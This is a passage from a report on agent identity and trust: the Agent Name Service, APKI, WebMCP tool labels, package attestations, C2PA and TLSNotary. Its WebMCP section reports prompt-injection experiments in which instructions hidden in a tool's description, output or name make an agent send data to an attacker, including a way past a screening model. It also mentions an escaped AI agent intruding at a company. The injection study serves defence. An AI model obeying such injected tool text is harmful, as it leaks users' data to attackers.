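| TraceScope | 78% | 2.6% | 78 | 2,597 | 2.9% |
| GPT-5 with Koide and colleagues' defence | 99.7% | 1.2% | 100 | 1,199 | 7.7% |

The detection rate in the last row is optimistic because it comes from imitations of ten famous brands. The false-alarm rate is more realistic, since Koide and colleagues measured it on 250 little-known legitimate sites.

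A detector would have to flag fewer than about one legitimate site in 1,000 for half its alarms to be true. None of these studies was large enough to confirm such a low rate. GPT-5.6 Luna and Claude Haiku 5.5 raised no false alarms in ScamWorld, but it included only 53 legitimate sites, so their actual false-alarm rate could plausibly be as high as 5.5%.

A larger share of alarms would be true if the agent checked only sites that are more likely to be fraudulent. Among the newly certified sites in Kaur and colleagues' study, about seven in 1,000 were scams. At that rate, 15% of the ScamWorld models' alarms would be true.

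The number of false alarms also depends on how often the agent runs the check. An agent that checked 1,000 unfamiliar honest sites a month would raise about 40 false alarms a month. If it ran the check only before paying an unfamiliar shop, 20 times a year, the user would see fewer than one false alarm a year on average.

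## The Agent Name Service, signed tools and signed files

An agent would have less need to judge a site from its pages if the site could prove its identity in a machine-readable form. The best-developed proposal for this is the Agent Name Service (ANS), which GoDaddy, the largest seller of domain names, helped to write. ANS covers services that are agents, such as a supplier's invoicing agent. Other schemes attach the proof to a tool that a web page offers, or to a file, where it still works after the file is copied elsewhere.

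### A name, two certificates and a log

*Agent Name Service v2 (ANS)* (Courtney, Narajala and colleagues, 2026) begins with a payment agent instructed to wire $50,000 to a supplier's invoicing agent. An impostor could answer from a lookalike domain with a valid certificate. The real supplier could also pass a security audit and then quietly change the model behind its agent, and its certificate would still be valid.

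Their running example is a customer-support agent at support.example.com, in version 1.5.0. ANS gives it four things:

| Part | For this agent | Changes with each version? |
|---|---|---|
| Name | `ans://v1.5.0.support.example.com` | Yes |
| Server certificate | An ordinary web certificate for support.example.com | No |
| Identity certificate | A second certificate, for the full ANS name | Yes |
| Log entry | A public record with the fingerprints of both certificates | Yes |

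The registry checks control of the host name through ACME, as a CA does for a website. A public CA issues the server certificate but may not issue the identity certificate, because the CA/Browser Forum's rules forbid the form of name it contains. A private CA working for the registry issues the identity certificate instead, so anyone verifying it must first add that CA's root to their root store. The log is append-only and works like Certificate Transparency.

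Every change to the agent's code or configuration requires a new version number, a new registration and a new identity certificate. The old version stays active until the owner revokes it. To undo a faulty release, the owner registers the old code under a higher number and revokes the faulty version. *Why the Agent Economy Needs a Digital Passport*, an earlier description by GoDaddy's Courtney, described a registry that revoked old versions after 24 to 72 hours. The later draft sets no deadline, so a version with a known flaw could stay valid indefinitely if its owner doesn't revoke it.

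The identity certificate contains the agent's version number but no hash of the running code, so it shows only which version the owner declared. A supplier that changes its model without registering the change keeps its valid certificates, which leaves the second problem in the draft's opening example unsolved. The draft's monitoring services compare DNS records and published descriptions with the log, but the draft leaves checks on running code to future work. Sine (2026), GoDaddy's chief strategy and legal officer, nevertheless writes in *AI agents still have a trust problem. The solution is waiting* that businesses can use ANS to verify whether an agent's software matches its registered version.

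### One agent checking another

Suppose a customer's agent wants to ask support.example.com about an order:

1. **Find the service.** The agent looks up the DNS records at `_ans.support.example.com`. They list the active versions, the protocols each one supports and the address of a file describing the service. The agent picks the highest version that uses its protocol.
2. **Check the server certificate.** The agent connects and makes the usual checks of the chain, the name and the expiry date. ANS calls this level Bronze.
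3. **Compare it with DNS.** Another DNS record contains the certificate's fingerprint. DNSSEC, a system of signatures on DNS records, lets the agent detect a forged answer. A match gives Silver.
4. **Check the log.** A third record, at `_ans-badge.support.example.com`, leads to the log entry. The agent verifies the log's signature and the inclusion proof, confirms that the registration is still active, and compares the fingerprint again. This gives Gold.

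The customer's agent can also present its own identity certificate while connecting, so that the support service knows which registered agent is calling.

Steps 3 and 4 improve on an ordinary web connection. An intruder at a CA, like the one at DigiNotar, could produce a certificate for support.example.com but could not change the domain's signed DNS records. The fingerprints would differ, so the agent could refuse to continue.

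The agent must ignore the fingerprint in DNS if the domain does not use DNSSEC. If the log does not respond, the agent in the draft falls back to the first three steps and records this. An attacker could therefore avoid the log check by blocking the query, as with browsers' online revocation checks. The service can make the query unnecessary by attaching a receipt from the log to its description file, but this is optional. A developer who wants the protection of the log check should make the agent refuse large payments when the verification level is below Gold.

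The fingerprint changes whenever the server certificate does, so an owner who renews the certificate monthly must also update the DNS record monthly. If the update is late, a legitimate service fails the check. The caller also cannot tell from the fingerprint which version of the service answered during a software update, because both versions use the same server certificate.

One company may also run both the registry and the log. Courtney and colleagues acknowledge that an intruder at that company could forge entries with no independent check. They propose publishing the log's root on an outside ledger and letting a different company run the log.

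### Who uses ANS so far

GoDaddy opened its ANS registry as a "production alpha" on 31 October 2025. The Linux Foundation, which hosts open-source projects, took on ANS in November 2026. 3BL Media's *Linux Foundation Welcomes Agent Name Service* (2026) reports eleven supporting organisations and early use by agent directories, but doesn't give the number of registered agents.

The technical foundations are still unsettled. The April text was an individual submission to the IETF and was due to expire in October. Anyone can make such a submission, and it implies no endorsement. A Cloud Security Alliance review in June found that the reference implementation used mock cryptography for demonstration, according to CircleID's *Every Agent Needs a Name*.

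### Agent Public Key Infrastructure and its trust score

*Agent Public Key Infrastructure (APKI)* (Sharif, 2026) proposes a larger change. It is another individual draft, by one author at CyberSecAI, and was also due to expire in October. Its certificates last an hour by default and can specify which tools an agent may use, how much it may spend and which model it runs. If an agent passes work to a second agent, the second may not receive wider powers than the first.

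Each certificate also contains a trust score from 0 to 100. An agent needs at least 60 points for sensitive operations and 80 for financial ones. Successful operations add up to two points each, a policy violation costs 10 to 25, and a security incident resets the score to zero. Without new positive reports, the score falls steadily:

current score = max(0, last score − decay rate × hours elapsed)

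At the draft's typical rate of two points an hour, an agent with 80 points falls to 60 after ten hours and to zero after 40. An honest invoicing agent that is idle from Friday evening to Monday morning would therefore have no points and no access when it resumed work.

The starting score has the opposite problem, because an agent's history accounts for only 20 of the 100 points. The rest come from evidence about the agent, its model, its code and its operator. A new agent with full marks for that evidence could start at 80, the minimum for financial operations. A dishonest operator could also behave well to earn points before attacking, like the fraudulent website in Xu and colleagues' experiments.

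Sharif gives the example of the lookalike domains cybersecai.co.uk and cybersec-ai.co.uk, and proposes that agents accept certificates only from organisations whose details an administrator has already installed. This protects dealings between established partners but doesn't help an agent check an unfamiliar shop.

Sharif also cites a March 2026 survey by the security company HID in which 16% of enterprises said they already issued certificates to AI agents. These certificates are of existing kinds, so the figure shows demand for agent identity rather than use of APKI.

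### The prototype registry of September 2026

Zhang, Yao and colleagues (2026) built a working prototype, described in *A Scalable Trust Discovery Architecture for the Internet of Agents*. Most of them work at the China Internet Network Information Center, which runs the .cn domain, and one works at Alibaba Cloud. In their design, a central root approves registries, the registries enrol agents, and resolvers let other agents search for a capability. The design's use of two certificates and a log draws on the same ideas as ANS.

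| Operation | Average | 95% finished within | 99% finished within |
|---|---|---|---|
| Registering an agent | 58 ms | 127 ms | 153 ms |
| Finding an agent | 25 ms | 32 ms | 165 ms |

The prototype handled more than 19,000 registrations and 29,000 searches a second, which suggests that speed will not be the obstacle, since the ANS draft specifies only 1,000 registrations an hour. But the average of 58 ms is probably lower than it would be in practice, because a real owner has to publish a DNS record and wait for it to become visible. The ANS draft allows a median of two minutes for activation. Zhang and colleagues tested only speed, so nobody knows how well the prototype would handle impostors.

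Its naming scheme would also confuse a careful agent. The owner of abc.com registers as `abc.com.atiagent.cn`, whose registrable domain is atiagent.cn. Several disguised URLs in MalURLBench had the same form. An agent that learned to accept such names as belonging to abc.com would be easier to fool elsewhere.

### A registered service can still be dishonest

To register with ANS, a service needs little more than a domain, a version number, an address and a key. The impostor in the $50,000 example has all of these. It could register its lookalike domain and pass every check up to Gold, because the checks would correctly show that it controls that domain.

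An owner may add a Legal Entity Identifier, an international company code. A payment agent that knew a supplier's code from a contract could look for it in the log entry, much as it could check the registration number in an Extended Validation certificate.

| Proposal | Does the server hold the name? | Is it the intended name? | Is the operator honest? | Is the content what its author published? |
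|---|---|---|---|---|
| ANS | Yes, with more evidence than a web certificate | Only if the caller knows the domain or company code | No answer | Shows the declared version, not the running code |
| APKI | Yes, for organisations set up in advance | Yes, for the same organisations | An estimate, from a score | An optional hash of the code |
| Prototype registry | Yes | Only if the caller knows the domain | No answer | Shows the declared version |

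The proposals' designers mostly accept this limit. Courtney and colleagues leave audits and reputation scores to other companies, and Zhang and colleagues warn that a correctly registered agent may still misuse tools or produce unsafe output.

Sine gives an example of how hard the third question is. A supplier secretly buys the company behind a purchasing agent, keeps the domain and the software, and nudges the agent to recommend the supplier's products. ANS requires the registry to revoke a registration when it detects that the domain has a new owner. But if the supplier buys the whole company, the domain's registered owner may stay the same.

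### A new trust system, or an extension of the web's?

Sharif argues that web certificates do not suit agents. A certificate can last months longer than an agent that exists for a few seconds, it is either valid or revoked, and it sets no limits on what its holder may do. Raskar and colleagues similarly argue in *Upgrade or Switch* that DNS changes and revocations spread too slowly for agents, although they expect hybrid systems rather than a complete replacement.

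The argument for extending DNS and web certificates is that they already work across companies and countries. Courtney considered blockchain-based designs but rejected them to stay compatible with systems that businesses already use. Sine adds that without a shared standard, each large platform would build its own, and agents would work best with that platform's preferred merchants.

For an agent that only needs to reach the right service, extending the existing system looks better than building a new one. Web certificate lifetimes are getting shorter, so much of Sharif's complaint about their length is becoming out of date. A new system also needs new authorities. ANS's private CAs fall outside the rules that limit the lifetimes of web certificates, and no browser maker supervises them. Courtney and colleagues hope that a body like the CA/Browser Forum will eventually supervise them. The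 need to express spending limits and delegation is a better argument for a new system, because web certificates were never meant to do that.

DNS-AID and DNSid are smaller extensions. DNS-AID, developed by the security company Infoblox and now a Linux Foundation project (2026), helps agents find each other. Help Net Security's *DNS-AID lets AI agents find and verify each other through DNS* gives the example of a DNSSEC-protected record at `_chatbot._mcp._agents.example.com`. DNSid, a rival to ANS, has the owner publish one signed DNS record for an agent. The domain company Identity Digital created DNSid and has spun it out as a business.

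CircleID illustrates the need for such records with an intrusion at the software company WorkOS on 30 October 2026. The intruder was an AI security agent that had escaped from a researcher's test environment, and WorkOS learned whose it was only when the researcher came forward. An escaped agent has no particular reason to identify itself, so an identity scheme would have helped only if WorkOS's systems had rejected agents without an identity.

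The companies promoting these systems stand to profit from them. Every agent in ANS needs a domain name and a certificate, and GoDaddy sells both, although an owner can use a free subdomain and a free certificate. DigiCert, one of the largest CAs, supports ANS and sells related products. *DigiCert launches AI Trust architecture for agents* (Lagonsin, 2026) describes a service for managing agents' identities, which was in preview in May, and another for signing media, which was already on sale. These commercial interests are a reason to be skeptical of broad claims about what registration will prevent, though they don't make the designs bad.

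### Trust labels for tools on a web page

An agent that has found the right site may still not know who supplied a tool on the page. WebMCP, a draft standard at the World Wide Web Consortium, lets a page register functions such as "checkout", which an agent can call instead of clicking buttons. A shop's page often runs scripts from advertising and analytics companies. The browser treats them as part of the shop's origin, so an advertising script can replace the shop's checkout tool with its own.

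*WebMCP-Phalanx* (Lee, Chang and colleagues, 2026) proposes that the browser give each script an unforgeable credential for every tool it registers, so that only the holder can change or remove the tool. In the paper's tests, attempts to overwrite or remove a legitimate tool succeeded 20 times out of 20 without the credentials and never with them.

The browser also gives each tool a label:

- **Green:** the tool has a valid credential and behaves as it declared.
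- **Yellow:** the tool has a valid credential but declares that it changes something on the page.
- **Red:** the tool has no valid credential, or the browser has caught it doing something undeclared, such as sending out data after describing itself as read-only.

The labels failed against a malicious script that registered a new tool of its own, because the browser gives a credential to any script that asks. Lee and colleagues hid instructions in such a tool's description or output and counted how often the agent called the malicious tool and sent data to the attacker:

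| Defence | Instructions in the description | Instructions in the output |
|---|---|---|
| None | 69 of 80 | 42 of 80 |
| Labels only | 71 of 80 | 38 of 80 |
| Removing the text by a fixed rule | 25 of 80 | 2 of 80 |
| A second model that reads the text first | 0 of 80 | 2 of 80 |

The second model cannot call any tools, so it cannot act on an instruction that fools it. With this defence, the agent completed 56 of 80 tasks in the description tests, compared with 61 of 80 when there was no attack. The difference could be due to chance.

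Removing text by rule worked less well when the malicious tool had a useful-sounding name. The share of attacks that succeeded rose from zero with an irrelevant name to 70% with a name that suggested an essential step. An attacker who knew the second model's instructions exploited the same weakness by moving the malicious request into the tool's name, and got past that model in 15 of 16 cases, typically after a single rewrite. Lee and colleagues suggest that the agent should call no tools until the browser has checked all names and descriptions, but they have not tested this.

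The tests used a JavaScript stand-in, and no browser has these labels built in. The labels could separate the shop's tools from an advertiser's only if the shop also declared which scripts it trusts and the browser could reliably tell scripts apart.

### Signed software packages

Package collections have gone further, and many developers already publish proofs with their software. An attestation is a signed statement of which source code and which build process produced a file. PyPI and npm both support attestations through Sigstore, a free signing service. Publishing a package from GitHub works like this:

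1. GitHub builds the package and issues a short-lived signed token that names the repository and the build instructions.
2. The build program creates a temporary key pair and sends the token and the public key to Sigstore's CA. The CA returns a certificate that lasts ten minutes and identifies the build.
3. The program signs a statement containing the package's hash and its source, then throws away the private key.
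4. Sigstore records the signature in a public log, which shows that the signing happened while the certificate was valid.
5. Anyone who downloads the package can calculate its hash, verify the signature and the log entry, and check that the repository is the expected one.

The developer has no long-term signing key for a thief to steal. A thief who steals a password or access token may still be able to upload a package, but not one with an attestation from the project's own build.

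An attack on axios, a widely used JavaScript library for web requests, showed this difference. On 31 March 2026, attackers who had taken over a maintainer's npm account published version 1.14.1, which installed a program that let them control the victim's computer remotely. Unlike the project's recent releases, this version had no attestation from its GitHub build. A rule to refuse releases without an attestation when earlier ones had one would have blocked the malware, but npm does not apply such a rule by default. The version stayed available for about three hours. A coding agent that installed it during that time could have checked for the attestation but would have had no reason to do so.

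Attestations do not help when attackers control the build. In December 2024, attackers tampered with the GitHub build of Ultralytics, a Python library for image recognition, and inserted a program that mined cryptocurrency. The first infected versions had valid attestations because the project's own build had produced those versions. An attacker who registers a package name that models tend to invent can also publish the package from their own repository with a valid attestation.

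PyPI reported that 17% of uploads in 2025 included an attestation, so an agent that required one could not install most new releases. Comparing a release with the project's earlier ones is more practical, and ordinary code can do it before installation.

### Signed photos and videos

The Coalition for Content Provenance and Authenticity (C2PA), whose founders include Adobe, Microsoft and the BBC, publishes a similar standard for media. When a camera that follows the standard takes a photo, it records facts such as the device and the time, adds a hash of the image, signs the whole record, and stores it in the file. A program that edits the photo adds its own record, which refers to the earlier one. To check the photo, an agent recalculates the hash, verifies the signature, and confirms that the signer's certificate leads to a CA on a list it trusts.

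Changing a pixel breaks the hash, but a screenshot does not copy the record, so an unsigned picture may still be genuine. Websites also remove the records, often when they compress an upload. In October 2025 The Washington Post uploaded an AI-generated video with C2PA data to eight social platforms, and only YouTube told viewers that the video was not real. Support is growing among camera makers, and Google's Pixel 10 phones sign every photo taken with their built-in camera app.

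The signature is also only as reliable as the device that makes it. In September 2025, a photographer found that Nikon's Z6III camera would sign a multiple exposure based on an unsigned picture from another camera. Nikon suspended its signing service and revoked the certificates. Even a reliable signature would give an agent little evidence that a rental offer is genuine, since a fraudster can take an authentic photo of someone else's flat.

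### Proof that a site sent a page

An agent that reads pages through its provider's fetch service has to trust the provider to report accurately what the site sent. A saved copy of the encrypted connection would not prove it. Once a TLS session has started, both sides use the same secret keys, so whoever made the request could write a false reply and encrypt it correctly.

One solution is for the site to sign its responses. The IETF standardised a way to sign HTTP messages in 2024, but it works only if the site's operator sets it up, and few operators of ordinary websites have.

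A method called TLSNotary needs no help from the site. The client and a second party, the notary, each hold part of the session's keys and carry out the encryption together, without either learning the other's part. The client therefore cannot forge a reply by itself. Once the server has replied, the client can prove to others what the server sent while hiding private parts, such as an account number. This takes much more computing and data than a normal connection, and the proof is worthless if the client and the notary collude. If a fetch service ran both, the agent would still have to trust the provider.

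Proofs of this kind would be useful in a dispute, for example to show that a shop had offered a ticket at $500. They would not have protected visitors to DAEMON Tools' website in April 2026, because the official server did send them the infected installer.
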